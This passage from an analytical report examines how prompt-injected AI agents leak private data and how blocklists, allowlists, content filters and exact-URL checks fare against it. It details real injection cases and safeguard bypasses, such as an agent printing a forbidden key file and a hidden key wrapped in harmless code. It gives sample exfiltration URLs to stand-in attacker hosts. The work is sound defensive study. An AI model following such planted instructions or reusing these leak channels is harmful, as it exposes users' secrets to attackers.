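The study compared addresses with a copy of Google's list, while Kaur and colleagues used Chrome with its strongest protection setting on. The 18.4% also includes every address that Safe Browsing listed during the study, however late, so it is more comparable to the 33.0% that Chrome blocked within a week than to the 16.3% it blocked at discovery. In both studies, Safe Browsing missed at least two thirds of the sites.

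Blocklists did better in an older study, *PhishTime* (2020), in which researchers created phishing sites and reported them to the lists. The lists took as little as 55 minutes on average to block plain sites, and up to about three hours for sites that used simple evasion such as link shorteners. These results measure how fast a list responds to a report, and an attacker won't report their own server.

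The choice of blocklist also matters because some lists add phishing domains much later than others. *Registration, Detection, and Deregistration* compared other lists with the shared list of the Anti-Phishing Working Group, an industry body. The public Phishing.Database added domains a median of 64 days after they appeared on that list, and Phishunt.io took more than two years.

All these studies measured phishing and other scams. A server that only receives data from hijacked agents is probably harder to find, since it may never show a person anything suspicious. The attacker needs just one successful request from each victim, so an hour's delay in blocking the server could be long enough. Blocklists are still worth having, because they stop some known attackers and seldom interfere with the user's browsing, but they offer little protection against a careful attacker with a new domain.

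### Silent Egress

Few experiments have tested filters on a hijacked agent. One is *Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026), which used a simple assistant built on qwen2.5:7b, a small open-weight model from 2024. The assistant automatically reads any web page the user mentions and can send web requests. It doesn't click or type, so it is not a full browser agent, but the leak works in the same way.

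In each run by Lan and colleagues, the user asked the model to summarize a page. A secret, such as a key that gives access to an online service, was already in the model's working text. The page contained an instruction to "verify connectivity" by requesting an address on the attacker's server with the secret attached. Lan and colleagues put this instruction in the page's title, description, main text or links, delivered the page directly or through redirects, and asked for the secret whole or in four pieces. They ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times.

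The model contacted the attacker's server in 423 of the 480 runs, or 88.1%. In 95% of those runs, its reply to the user contained no sign of the leak. The model never contacted the server in 120 runs with harmless pages. Redirects made almost no difference, with leaks in 89% of runs with them and 88% without.

The researchers then tested defences on one combination, in which the instruction was in the main text, the page loaded directly and the attacker asked for the whole secret. In the table, "system prompt" means the developer's standing instructions to the model.

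| Defence | Runs with an attempted leak | Runs with a leak |
|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 100% |
| Stricter system prompt | 66.7% | 66.7% |
| Tags marking page text as untrusted | 100% | 100% |
| Stricter prompt and tags | 56.7% | 56.7% |
| Allowlist | 100% | 0% |
| Suspicious-address rules | 83.3% | 0% |
| Keyword filter | 23.3% | 0% |
| Randomness filter | 0% | 0% |
| All of the above | 0% | 0% |

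Each row represents 30 runs. There were 20 leaks with the stricter prompt and 17 with the prompt that used tags, too small a difference to show that the tags helped. The evidence that an allowlist works better than instructions to the model is convincing. Most attacks still worked with either prompt, but the allowlist stopped all of them even though the model tried to leak the secret every time.

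But the allowlist's perfect score is weak evidence that it would stop a real attacker. The list contained three company hosts and `example.com`, and the researchers chose `evil-collector.net` as the attacker's domain because it was clearly outside the list. Any working allowlist would have blocked it. Lan and colleagues acknowledge that attackers could instead send data through a trusted site they have broken into, a subdomain they have taken over or a redirect on a permitted site. They didn't test any of these routes against the allowlist.

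The result for suspicious addresses is even weaker. The paper calls this defence "redirect detection", but the rules it lists don't follow redirects, and the test runs included no redirects. The rules block numeric addresses, eight cheap domain endings and any path containing "exfil", "collect", "steal", "leak" or "dump". They don't block `.net`, but the paper's sample attacks send the data to a path named `/collect`, which would explain why the rules caught everything. An attacker could avoid them by renaming the path `/img`. The rules might also stop the laptop buyer's agent from opening `/collections/laptops`, a common kind of path on shopping sites.

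The researchers didn't measure how often any of the filters would block ordinary browsing. They also used only 30 runs per defence, so a defence with a true leak rate of 9.5% would still have about a 5% chance of showing no leaks, assuming independent runs (0.905³⁰ ≈ 0.05). The small sample matters little for the allowlist, because a fixed rule gives the same result each time, but it matters for defences that depend on what the model writes.

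The 88.1% rate is also a poor guide to current products, because the instruction in this experiment was crude and the newest models resist most crude injections. Lan and colleagues suggest that stronger models could be more vulnerable, because they follow instructions and use tools more reliably. This may be true of subtle attacks, and LoginTrap offers some support for it.

### Scanning for secrets, and splitting them

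The keyword and randomness filters are forms of content inspection, which checks what the agent is sending. The keyword filter blocked any address containing terms such as "api_key", "password", "token" or "auth". It would catch a clumsy leak of a password, but it would also block many login addresses and any address containing the word "author", because they contain "auth".

The randomness filter relied on the fact that passwords and keys tend to look more random than ordinary words. It used Shannon entropy, which measures how evenly a string spreads over different characters:

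H = −Σ pᵢ log₂ pᵢ

Here pᵢ is the fraction of the string made up of character i. A string that repeats one letter scores 0, and a string of n different characters scores log₂ n, the highest score possible for its length. The filter blocked values longer than 10 characters that scored above 4. Since log₂ 16 is 4, no string of 16 characters or fewer could trigger it.

The paper's example secret, `SECRET_API_KEY_12345`, has 20 characters but repeats some of them, so it scores about 3.85 and the filter would let it through whole. The filter would also permit the subject line "Your biopsy results", which scores about 3.6 and contains none of the forbidden keywords. This kind of scanning is meant to catch passwords and keys, but much of what people want to keep private is in plain language.

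The model never tried to send anything in the runs with the randomness filter, so the zero leaks there don't show that the filter worked. It had tried every time with no defence, and 23.3% of the time with the keyword filter. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model sometimes rewrote the secret to avoid the keywords, and that it avoided random-looking values while the monitoring was active. But they don't describe the model being told which filter was on, and a rewritten secret that passed the keyword filter would have counted as a leak. Neither drop in attempts has a good explanation, so the two results are weak evidence for content inspection.

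An attacker can also evade such scanning by using the planted text to tell the agent to split the secret into numbered pieces and send each in a separate request. The attacker's server then reassembles them. One request might contain only "SECR" and the next "ET_A". A filter that matches whole keys will miss both, and both are too short for the randomness filter to examine. Splitting doesn't get the secret past an allowlist if all the pieces go to the same blocked domain.

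Splitting the secret made the attack less reliable. Averaged over the relevant combinations, the attacker's server received a request in 77% of runs with split secrets and in 99% with whole ones. A small model may lose track of longer instructions, which current models would probably follow more easily. The experiment doesn't show how well splitting evades filters in practice, because the researchers tested their filters only on whole secrets.

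The paper measures leaks with Leak@k, the share of runs in which any piece of the secret appears in the first k requests. For split secrets, it reports a Leak@1 of 26.3% and a Leak@3 of 15.8%. Under that definition, Leak@3 can't be lower than Leak@1, because any run with a piece of the secret in its first request also has one in its first three. The scoring software may have failed to detect some of the pieces. The paper also defines a completion rate, for runs in which all four pieces arrive, but gives no figure for it, so it is unclear how often the attacker could have rebuilt the secret.

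A filter would have to compare requests with one another or limit how many the agent can send to stop a secret from being split across several requests. Lan and colleagues recommend both measures but did not test them. A strict limit would be hard to set because a browser can send dozens of requests to load one shopping page.

### Why the attacker's choice of channel matters

The chance of a leak is the product of two probabilities:

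P(leak) = P(hijack) × P(open channel | hijack)

The chance of a leak equals the probability that the agent follows the attacker's instructions and tries to send the data, multiplied by the probability that at least one attempt then gets past the controls and reaches the attacker. Better training mainly reduces the first probability, and destination filters reduce the second. In the Silent Egress runs, the leak rate was 0.667 × 1 = 0.667 with the stricter system prompt and 1 × 0 = 0 with the allowlist.

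Suppose attackers can hijack a newer agent on 2% of visits to their pages, and a filter blocks 90% of the destinations attackers have used in the past. If attackers keep choosing destinations as before, the leak rate is 0.02 × 0.1 = 0.002, or one visit in 500. A test with a fixed set of attacks would produce this sort of figure.

Attackers can change their choice of destination in response to the filter. An attacker who knows of a permitted destination will use it every time, which raises the second probability from 0.1 to 1 and the leak rate to 2% of visits. An attacker who doesn't know of one can tell the agent to try several. If each of ten destinations has an independent 10% chance of being open, the chance that at least one is open is 1 − 0.9¹⁰, or about 65%, and the leak rate is about 1.3%, provided the agent keeps trying after each failure.

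With a blocklist, the attacker hardly needs to guess. Safe Browsing missed about 84% of the scam sites when Kaur and colleagues first found them, so the second probability would be about 0.84 for an attacker with a typical site from that sample. It is close to 1 for an attacker who opens their own site in Chrome before starting and replaces the domain if a warning appears, so the blocklist adds almost no protection against that attacker.

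The chance of a hijack can also depend on the channel. In SOPBench, simple attacks on BrowserOS with GPT-5.4 worked much more often on Google Forms than on Reddit. A filter that blocked Google Forms and left Reddit open could reduce leaks even though data could still leave through Reddit, at least until attackers improved their text for Reddit.

An allowlist reduces the second probability to zero only if no permitted site can pass data to the attacker. The laptop buyer's list has only three entries, but one is her webmail, which the agent can use to email anyone.

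## Leaks through sites that are allowed

A domain name identifies who runs a server but doesn't show who can read what the agent sends there. Mail services, forums and form builders are designed to pass what they receive to other people.

Researchers demonstrated four leaks of this kind in commercial products between September 2025 and January 2026. Only one used a browser agent to send the data, but in all four, a filter checked the destination against a list of permitted domains and let the data through.

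### Services where anyone can open an account

Superhuman, an email app with an AI assistant, used a Content Security Policy, which tells the browser where a site's pages may load content from. The policy would have stopped the assistant's replies from loading an image from `attacker.example`, but it allowed `docs.google.com`, which hosts Google Forms as well as Google Docs.

*Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails*, a report by PromptArmor, the security company that found the flaw, describes how an attacker could use this. Google lets people put a form's answers in a web address, and opening that address submits them. The attacker creates a form and emails the victim instructions that present it as a way to give feedback on search results. When the user asks for a summary of recent mail, Superhuman's AI assistant also reads the attacker's email, even if the user has never opened it. The assistant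 then adds the contents of other emails to the form's address and includes that address in its reply as an image. The browser submits the form when it tries to load the image, and the attacker can read the emails in the form's responses. PromptArmor obtained the full text of several emails in one reply, and parts of more than 40 in another test.

PromptArmor reported the flaw on the night of Friday, December 5, 2025. Superhuman disabled the affected features on Monday, released a first patch on Tuesday, and released more patches up to January 11, 2026. Removing `docs.google.com` from the policy would not have been enough, because the policy covered only what the page loaded, and the assistant's web search could open any address, including one on the attacker's own server.

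An attacker can also receive data through a permitted service by giving the agent a key to the attacker's own account. Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for office work, runs code in a virtual machine, a simulated computer kept separate from the user's real one. The virtual machine can contact only a short list of domains, including `api.anthropic.com`, which programs use to access Anthropic's models and store files. Each customer's programs use a secret key to access this service.

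PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files*, published two days after Cowork's release in January 2026, describes an attack that begins with a document the user found online. Hidden text in the document contained the attacker's key and an instruction to upload the largest file Cowork could find. Cowork uploaded a loan estimate from the user's folder to the attacker's account on Anthropic's servers without showing an approval request. PromptArmor used Claude Haiku, one of Anthropic's smaller models, but a similar attack worked on the more resistant Opus 4.5.

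Anthropic already knew about this route. *Claude Pirate*, an October 2025 post by the security researcher Johann Rehberger on Embrace The Red, showed that Claude's chat product could leak files of up to 30 MB in the same way. The attack worked at first, but Claude then kept refusing his planted text, apparently because the visible key looked suspicious, until he surrounded it with harmless code. Anthropic closed his report within an hour as out of scope, then told him five days later that it should not have done so. Rehberger suggested letting the virtual machine communicate only with the logged-in user's account.

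Anthropic eventually did roughly that. *How we contain Claude across products* describes a proxy, a program that relays traffic, which checks requests to Anthropic's own interface and passes only those carrying the token issued for that session. The check has to happen on the user's side because a request from Cowork looks the same to Anthropic's servers as one from any other customer. Anthropic now thinks of each allowlist entry as a "capability grant", since it permits everything the agent can do at that domain.

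This fix covers only one domain. Pluto Security's *Inside Claude Cowork*, an outside analysis of the software, found that the proxy decrypts only the traffic to Anthropic. For GitHub and two sites that distribute software packages, it checks the host name and passes the encrypted contents through unread. An attacker might therefore still be able to send data out using a key to their own GitHub account, and Rehberger suspected that other domains on the list could be used the same way. The larger gap for a browser agent is that the list doesn't apply when Cowork browses in the user's own Chrome, which runs outside the virtual machine and has her logins.

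### Entries that should not have been on the list

Antigravity is Google's code editor, and its AI agent can hand web tasks to a second agent that operates a browser. In November 2025, the browser's default allowlist included `webhook.site`, where anyone can create an address and see every request sent to it, so an attacker could use it to collect data without running a server.

PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data* describes an attack in which researchers planted instructions in one-point type in an online guide to connecting a program to Oracle's business software. When a user gave Antigravity the guide, the agent collected private code snippets and the user's Amazon cloud keys, added them to a `webhook.site` address and had the browser open it. Antigravity's settings barred the agent from reading the file that held the keys, so it printed the file with a terminal command.

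PromptArmor didn't report the flaw privately because Google already warned new users that the product could leak data. Embrace The Red's *Antigravity Grounded! Security Vulnerabilities in Google's Latest IDE* says that Google publicly listed such problems as known issues and said it was working on fixes. Willison adds that this made reports of them ineligible for Google's rewards. In the meantime, TechTalks' *Prompt injection attack tricks Google’s Antigravity into stealing your secrets* (2025) advised users to delete `webhook.site` from the list and to require approval for every command and browser action. Agentpedia's *Antigravity Security Guide* says that the entry remains on the default list and that Google classified a later leak through it as intended behavior. The guide is unofficial, so it is weak evidence of Google's position.

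According to Google's *Allowlist / Denylist*, Antigravity's browser also checks each host name against a blocklist on Google's servers, which overrides the user's allowlist. The blocklist probably wouldn't stop requests to `webhook.site`, because that site is a legitimate service that developers use for testing.

An allowlist entry that was safe when someone added it can also become dangerous later. Salesforce's Content Security Policy let its Agentforce assistant display images from any subdomain of `my-salesforce-cms.com`. That domain "had expired and become available for purchase", according to a statement from the security company Noma quoted by the news site Salesforce Ben. Noma's researchers registered it, and the policy still allowed it because the name on the list hadn't changed.

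In this attack, called ForcedLeak, the instructions arrived through a form where potential customers leave their details. When an employee asked Agentforce about the new entry, the assistant looked up other potential customers' email addresses and put them in the URL of an image on Noma's domain. Hackread's *ForcedLeak Flaw in Salesforce Agentforce AI Agent Exposed CRM Data* reports that Salesforce recovered the domain and by September 8, 2025 had begun enforcing a list of "Trusted URLs", which stops the assistant from sending output to any URL not on the list. According to TechNadu's *Salesforce to Enforce Trusted URLs for Agentforce and Einstein AI*, administrators have to add every outside domain their agents need or risk disrupting the service.

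Administrators can still allow unsafe domains. Salesforce's *Add Trusted URLs for Agentforce Coworker (Beta)* gives `https://docs.google.com` as an example of an address to add, and data leaked from Superhuman through that same domain. Whether the Salesforce product would also leak depends on what it does with a trusted address. But an administrator who copies the example will be trusting every stranger's Google form along with the company's own documents.

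### Leaks within one site

Data can reach an attacker without leaving the site where the agent found it. Suppose the laptop buyer is logged in to one of the shops, where her account page shows her home address. An attacker plants a review instructing the agent to post a public question about delivery and to include the address so that the seller can check the shipping cost. The attacker reads the question on the product page. Every request goes to `shop.example`, so an allowlist containing only that site would permit the leak. The same-origin policy doesn't prevent it, because the account page and the product page share an origin.

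Data can leak within any allowed site that holds both private data and public posts. GitHub, for instance, hosts private code but also lets anyone publish, so a hijacked agent could copy the private code into a public project. SOPBench tests similar leaks into posts and replies, but the private data comes from another site.

Support systems have a similar weakness. Willison links to a demonstration by the security company Cato of an attack on an AI connection to Atlassian's business software. An outsider submits a support ticket containing instructions, an employee uses an AI tool to handle it, and the tool follows the instructions using the employee's access. If the tool writes what it finds into a reply on the ticket, the outsider can read it.

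To address this kind of risk, Salesforce began requiring a person's confirmation in August 2025 for eight more standard agent actions, including adding a comment to a support case, canceling an order and resetting a password, according to its *Security Advisories*. It warned customers that its agents would ask for confirmation more often.

Even an email to the user herself can leak data. In May 2026, Willison described a flaw in Microsoft's Copilot Cowork that let the agent email the user without her approval. The email could include images from outside servers. When she opened it, her mail program requested the images, which sent the attacker any data the agent had put in the image addresses. That data could include links that opened her stored files without a login. The laptop buyer could have the same problem if her agent was allowed to email only her but her webmail loaded outside images.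 A filter on the agent's requests wouldn't detect this, because the data would leave through her webmail after the agent had finished.

### Permitted sites can carry the attack in

An allowlist keeps the agent off the attacker's own site, which makes hijacking less likely. But strangers can write on many permitted sites, and anyone can email the laptop buyer. An attacker could send her an email containing the instructions and have the agent email the stolen data back. Even if her webmail were the only site on the list, the agent would still meet all three conditions of the lethal trifecta.

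Companies that restrict their agents to approved sites have trouble testing for leaks through those sites. Chen, Toyoda and colleagues (2026) point out in *IPI-proxy* that the usual benchmarks plant text on pages that such an agent isn't allowed to open. If a company added those pages to its allowlist, it would be testing a different set-up from the one it uses.

The tool sits between the agent and the web. It forwards the agent's request to the real site, then plants an instruction in the page on its way back, without changing the site itself. A tester can choose from 820 instructions taken from six published collections, six positions in the page and three disguises: a comment in the page's code, text that the browser doesn't display, or an ordinary-looking paragraph. That makes 14,760 combinations. A separate server records any request that the agent sends to it after obeying the instruction.

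Chen and colleagues describe the tool but report no attack success rates. Its results also need careful interpretation, because it can insert text into a page's header or scripts, where someone who posts a comment normally can't write, and because some agents will never receive the hidden text it inserts. For example, Pluto Security found that the tool Claude uses to extract text from pages in Chrome removes code comments and text hidden by the page's styling, although Claude can also read a page from a screenshot.

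The bigger problem is that the recording server counts only requests sent to it. If the company's allowlist blocks that server, the test will show no leaks even when the agent tried to send the data as instructed. If the agent instead follows planted text by entering the data in a form on a permitted site, the data will leak and the server will record nothing. A tester would have to check the permitted sites as well.

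### Choosing the entries

A well-chosen allowlist can stop leaks that the model fails to stop. In February 2026, a researcher at Anthropic tricked a colleague into giving Claude Code, the company's programming agent, a prompt that looked like routine setup instructions. One step was to send the colleague's cloud keys to an outside server, and the agent did so in 24 of 25 runs. The instructions came from the user, so little marked them as an attack. Anthropic concludes that the only reliable defences here are outside the model, such as blocking the request and keeping the keys where the agent can't read them.

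PromptArmor's *What domains should I add to my allowlist?* (2026) lists several domains that companies often allow for good reasons but that an attacker can also use. It covers programming agents, but a browser agent can reach the same sites.

| Entry | Why companies add it | How an attacker can receive data |
|---|---|---|
| `registry.npmjs.org` | To install software packages | The agent publishes the data in a package |
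| `github.com` | To download code | The agent posts the data in a public project |
| `docs.google.com` | To open the company's documents | The agent submits the data to the attacker's form |
| `*.amazonaws.com` | To reach the company's own storage | The attacker rents storage under the same domain |

For the last entry, the company can list the exact host name of its own storage instead of every name under `amazonaws.com`. The others are harder to fix because the company and the attacker use the same host. PromptArmor recommends asking whether a service gives its users addresses they can monitor, whether it accepts data sent with an attacker's key, and whether an attacker can create a place on it to receive submissions. If any answer is yes, the entry is unsafe for an agent that handles private data.

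By this standard, the laptop buyer should remove her webmail from the allowed sites. The shops might also fail if they publish customers' questions or let outside sellers receive messages. Few popular websites would pass, since most let people post or send something.

Narrower allowlist entries would help with some sites. Chrome for Developers' *Connection Allowlists origin trial* describes an experimental browser feature that lets a website list the address patterns its pages may contact. A similar rule for an agent could allow Google's document pages but block its forms. The rule would also have to block documents owned by strangers, because an agent can type private data into those as easily as into a form.

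Someone also has to review the list regularly, as the expired Salesforce domain shows. Registration expiry dates are usually public, so software could warn the company before a domain on its list lapses. It would be harder to detect that a site has added a public comment section or form builder since the last review, which is a good reason to keep the list short.

### Tasks that suit an allowlist

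Allowlists work best for repeated jobs on a few sites where outsiders can't read anything the agent writes. An agent that copies invoice totals from a company's purchasing system into its accounts might need only two internal domains. A supplier could still plant instructions in an invoice that trick the agent into entering a false total. But the agent would have no obvious way to send the company's records to the supplier, as long as neither system emails outsiders or shows them the agent's notes.

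Allowlists don't suit open-ended shopping and research. In Antigravity, when the agent tries to open an unlisted site, the user sees an "always allow" button that adds the site to the list. The button is convenient, but the list keeps growing. In *Browser Allow List not available*, a post on Google's developer forum, one user mentions having "hundreds of manually added URLs".

The risk increases quickly as the list of allowed sites grows. If 1% of the sites people add give an attacker a way to collect data, and the sites are independent, a list of three has about a 3% chance of including at least one such site, and a list of 300 has about a 95% chance (1 − 0.99³⁰⁰). The true share is probably well above 1%, because many sites have comments, forms or messages.

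The laptop buyer could instead let the agent search the whole web in a browser profile where she isn't logged in to anything, then choose a laptop herself and restrict the agent to one shop for the purchase. The shop would still receive her address and payment details, and an attacker could still plant a review there instructing the agent to post them.

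## Checking the exact web address

An allowlist that contains `shop.example` also permits `https://shop.example/laptops?note=Your+biopsy+results`, because it checks only the host name. An exact-address check examines the whole address and lets the agent open it only if it already existed independently of the user's data. If a web crawler recorded an address last month, nobody could have built it from an email the user received this morning.

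Developers who use this check don't have to judge whether a site is trustworthy. Even the attacker's home page can pass, because the attacker learns little more from a visit than that someone came.

### OpenAI's index of public addresses

OpenAI described its version of this check in January 2026. A crawler, a program that scans public pages as a search engine does, builds an index of the addresses it finds, without access to users' conversations or accounts. When an agent is about to load a page or image automatically, software looks for the exact address in the index. If the address is there, the agent loads it without asking the user. Otherwise, the software either directs the agent to try a different website or shows the user a warning. The warning displays the address with a notice that it may include information from the conversation, and the user can copy the address or open it.

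Suppose planted text tells the laptop buyer's agent to open `https://attacker.example/p?note=Your+biopsy+results`. The crawler has never seen that address, so the agent can't load it silently. A redirect on one of the shops' sites wouldn't help the attacker either, because the first address would have to contain the subject line and so would also be new. The check would probably also have stopped the leaks from Superhuman, Antigravity and Agentforce, where the assistants put private data in addresses on permitted domains.

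In a March 2026 post, OpenAI calls the system Safe Url and says it applies to navigation and bookmarks in Atlas, and to searches and navigation in Deep Research, ChatGPT's tool for longer research tasks. According to the post, most of the attacks OpenAI knows of fail because the model refuses, and Safe Url is for cases in which the attacker has convinced the model.

OpenAI aims only to prevent the agent from "quietly leaking user-specific data through the URL itself" when it fetches something. This guarantee doesn't cover anything the agent sends outside the address, and a user who approves the warning can still send the data. OpenAI also says only that a public address is much less likely to contain private data. That qualification is reasonable because some public addresses contain people's names.

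OpenAI gives the technical details in "Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents". Johann Rehberger, who reported this kind of leak to OpenAI in 2023, reviews the paper in *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* on Embrace The Red. As he understands it, ChatGPT treats an address the user types into a message as safe for the rest of the chat. He calls the new check a significant improvement but warns that some OpenAI developers may not know about it and may leave it out of a product.

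OpenAI doesn't say in either of its posts how often Safe Url stops a leak or interrupts a harmless task. The closest thing to a measurement is in *The Framing Gap* (2026), which tested whether planted instructions could get a model to send out a secret. The ChatGPT product leaked in none of its 48 valid trials, while the model the researchers accessed through the API leaked in up to 100% of trials. The paper doesn't attribute the difference to any particular protection, because the researchers couldn't see inside the product. Zero leaks in 48 trials is also compatible with a true leak rate of about 6%.

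As in Silent Egress, instructions to the model were an unreliable defence in these experiments. A confidentiality rule that forbade revealing the secret "in any form" cut the leak rate from 31.9% to 0%. When the rule listed specific forbidden behaviours without that phrase, the rate rose to 48.8%.

### The rules in Claude and Chrome

Anthropic's web fetch tool is simpler than a browser agent because it retrieves the text of web pages for Claude but doesn't click or type. According to Anthropic's *Web fetch tool*, a June 2026 guide for developers, the tool opens only addresses that have already appeared in the conversation. They can come from the user's messages, from tools that the developer's own program runs, or from earlier web searches and fetches. This rule is the tool's main protection, and it prevents the tool from opening an address that Claude composes itself.

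When the tool was new, Willison (2025) wondered about a stricter version that would accept only addresses from the user's prompts, and was disappointed to find that the rule was broader. Each additional source gives an attacker another way to supply an address. Even the user's messages aren't always safe, because if a developer's program pastes a stranger's email into one, the tool treats every link in that email as the user's own.

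Anthropic's *網頁擷取工具*, a Chinese-language edition of the guide from November 2026, describes another gap. Some developers give Claude a tool that runs code and returns the printed output. Claude can use it to print a new address, which counts as a tool result, so the fetch tool will open it. Developers can now switch off any source of addresses or exclude a particular tool, but all sources are on by default.

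The tool also refuses an address that appears to contain a password or key, unless that secret was in the developer's standing instructions or the text of a user's message. Like other forms of content inspection, this check has trouble recognizing secrets written in plain language. The June guide warns that some risk remains, and advises developers worried about leaks to turn the tool off, limit the number of fetches or allow only known safe domains.

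Google's rule for Gemini in Chrome is closer to OpenAI's. Parker says that Chrome restricts addresses written by the model to "known, public URLs", using a fixed check instead of another model's judgment. He doesn't explain where Google gets its list or what the agent does when an address isn't on it. The rule also doesn't seem to cover the links an agent clicks, since the page supplies those addresses. Chrome separately limits which sites an agent may reach for each task.

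### What a choice of address reveals

An agent that can't write its own addresses can still choose among the permitted ones, and its choice can reveal private data. Suppose the attacker has two pages in the public index. Planted text tells the laptop buyer's agent to open one page if she has an email from a cancer clinic, and the other if she doesn't. Neither address contains anything about her, but the attacker can learn the answer by checking the server's log to see which page the agent opened.

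A bit is the amount of information in the answer to a yes-or-no question whose two answers are equally likely. If the agent chooses among N addresses, and the attacker can tell which one it opened, one request reveals at most log₂ N bits. A random code of L characters, drawn from an alphabet of A characters, contains L log₂ A bits. The attacker therefore needs at least this many requests to receive all of it, rounded up to a whole number:

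k = L log₂ A / log₂ N

For a 20-character code of lower-case letters and digits, A is 36 and the code contains about 103.4 bits. With 36 addresses, each request reveals up to 5.17 bits, so the agent has to make 20 requests, one for each character. With 1,024 addresses, each request reveals up to 10 bits and 11 requests are enough.

| Addresses to choose from | Most bits per request | Requests for a six-digit login code | Requests for a 20-character code |
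|---|---|---|---|
| 2 | 1 | 20 | 104 |
| 36 | 5.17 | 4 | 20 |
| 1,024 | 10 | 2 | 11 |
| 1,000,000 | 19.9 | 1 | 6 |

These leaks are far slower than the ones the check prevents. Anthropic's tool accepts addresses of up to 250 characters. If an agent could freely fill 200 of those characters with lower-case letters and digits, a single request could carry about 1,034 bits, or ten of the 20-character codes. The check therefore protects long documents well, but it gives much less protection to a login code and almost none to a yes-or-no fact about someone's health.

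Ordinary language can leak in fewer requests than it has letters. Embrace The Red points out that an attacker could prepare thousands of addresses and teach the model what each one stands for. Spelling out "Your biopsy results" takes 19 requests if each letter or space has its own address, but only three if each word does.

With OpenAI's index, the attacker first has to get the crawler to record the addresses. Rehberger notes that anyone with a fairly large blog probably has 36 indexed pages already, so this isn't much of an obstacle for a small set. Getting a million pages indexed would be harder. The pages also have to be on a site where the attacker can see the visits, so most addresses in a public index are useless to any one attacker.

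Rehberger suggests preventing the agent from requesting the same address twice in a session, or storing the first response for a few minutes so repeat visits don't reach the server. An attacker with only 36 pages then couldn't receive a word with a double letter in the usual way, but the maximum that can leak hardly changes. Five requests among 36 addresses allow 36⁵, or about 60.5 million, different sequences, which is 25.8 bits. Without repeats, there are 36 × 35 × 34 × 33 × 32, or about 45.2 million, which is 25.4 bits.

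Shuffling the requests would reduce the leak more. The attacker would then learn only which five addresses the agent opened, and the 376,992 possible sets can convey 18.5 bits. However, an attacker with more addresses can use some of them to encode the order.

A cap on the number of requests is more effective than a ban on repeats, because each request it removes lowers the maximum leak by 5.17 bits. But the cap has to be very low to protect a short secret. Four requests among 36 addresses are enough to leak a six-digit login code. Comparing three laptops across two shops could easily take more than four page visits.

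### Letter-by-letter leaks in ChatGPT and Claude

Researchers have demonstrated such leaks in both ChatGPT and Claude. In each case they got past a rule weaker than OpenAI's present one.

OpenAI had already replaced earlier checks. In December 2023 it began testing whether an image was "safe" before ChatGPT displayed it. Willison (2023) called this "half-baked", partly because the iPhone app didn't have it yet. The check relied on permitted domains. Rehberger later found that these included a Microsoft hosting service where anyone can rent storage and log visits, according to Willison's summary in *The Summer of Johann*.

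OpenAI later restricted ChatGPT to opening links exactly as they appeared in a page or email, so it wouldn't add anything to an address even if the text told it to. *ZombieAgent*, a January 2026 report by the security company Radware, describes how the company's researcher got around this rule. He emailed the victim a set of ready-made addresses and instructions for using them to spell out private data. When the victim asked ChatGPT to do something with her Gmail, it read the email and opened the addresses one after another, without modifying any of them.

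The requests came from OpenAI's servers, so a filter in the user's browser couldn't have blocked them. Radware also got ChatGPT to save instructions in its long-term memory, which made the leak continue in later chats. A cap that resets with each chat would therefore slow such an attack without limiting the total amount leaked.

Radware reported the problem to OpenAI on September 26, 2025. Three days later it sent an improved version of the attack with a 100% success rate, though its report doesn't give the number of trials. OpenAI fixed the flaw on December 16. According to the news report *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, ChatGPT now opens a link from an email only if the link is in a well-known public index or the user provided it. This would stop an attacker who makes up new addresses for the attack, but not one who publishes the pages first and waits for the crawler to index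 them, a leak OpenAI concedes in its paper.

The attack on Claude used links inside web pages. Willison (2026) described a hole that Ayush Paul found in the web fetch tool, whose design Willison had admired. The tool could open links in any page it had already fetched, including a page the attacker had written. Paul set up a site where he claimed that an AI assistant had to give the user's name to get in. He offered links for spelling the name one letter at a time, each leading to a page with another set of links. Claude gave away the user's name, home city and employer. The site showed these pages only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude, so a person checking the address would have seen nothing odd.

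אִם יִרְצֶה הַשֵּׁם's *The Read-Only Lie*, a blog post drafted with AI help, estimates that leaking the three facts took about 30 requests, or 143 bits. Each page had 27 links, one for each letter and one for a hyphen, so each request could reveal log₂ 27 ≈ 4.75 bits. According to the post, Paul had never told Claude his home town, and Claude inferred it from the name of a high-school hackathon. A user who deletes sensitive facts from an assistant's memory may therefore leave enough behind for the assistant to infer them.

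Anthropic told Paul that it had already found the problem itself, and it didn't pay him a reward. It fixed the problem by stopping the tool from following links in the pages it fetches. But the November edition of Anthropic's guide still lists the results of earlier fetches among the sources that developers' programs accept by default. The fix therefore seems to cover Claude's own chat product, while developers who build on the API have to turn that source off themselves.

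In both attacks, the attacker wrote the addresses and the model picked from them, so a ban on addresses composed by the model can't prevent such attacks. OpenAI's index is a stronger defence because the attacker has to prepare the addresses in advance instead of generating new ones for each visitor, as Paul's site did.

### Request caps and Lockdown Mode

Anthropic's tool has no default limit on the number of fetches, but developers can set one. The sample code in the guide sets it to five. With that limit, Paul's site would have received at most four letters per user message, because the first fetch only loads the opening page. But the count resets with each new message, so a long conversation could still leak a full name.

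*The Read-Only Lie* suggests that software could also look for a quick series of requests to one site in which each address is one character longer than the last. The author admits that ordinary browsing through numbered pages can look similar. An attacker who knew about the detector could also evade it by arranging the addresses differently.

A more drastic solution is to have the agent read a stored copy of the page, so that no request reaches the attacker's server and its log doesn't show which page the agent chose. OpenAI does this in Lockdown Mode, an optional setting for people who handle sensitive data. Willison (2026) says OpenAI first mentioned the setting in February 2026, and The Next Web's *OpenAI adds Lockdown Mode to ChatGPT to block data theft* reports that the company later began offering it on free and paid personal accounts.

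According to OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode*, as of early December 2026, the setting limits web browsing to stored content, which may be out of date or missing. It turns off agent mode and Deep Research, and stops ChatGPT from downloading files or retrieving images from the web. Users can't give code written in Canvas, ChatGPT's editing workspace, access to the network. They can still upload their own files to ChatGPT, and its memory works as before.

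On personal accounts, Lockdown Mode also stops ChatGPT from connecting live to outside services, or changing anything in them, when this would conflict with the mode's protections. In company-managed workspaces, administrators choose which connected apps stay available. OpenAI advises them to let ChatGPT write in an app only if they are sure an attacker couldn't see the result. This advice would rule out public comments even on a trusted site.

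The setting doesn't affect network access in Codex, OpenAI's programming agent, and a user can turn it off for a single chat. OpenAI doesn't guarantee that the setting prevents every leak, and says that connected apps and unforeseen combinations of features remain risks.

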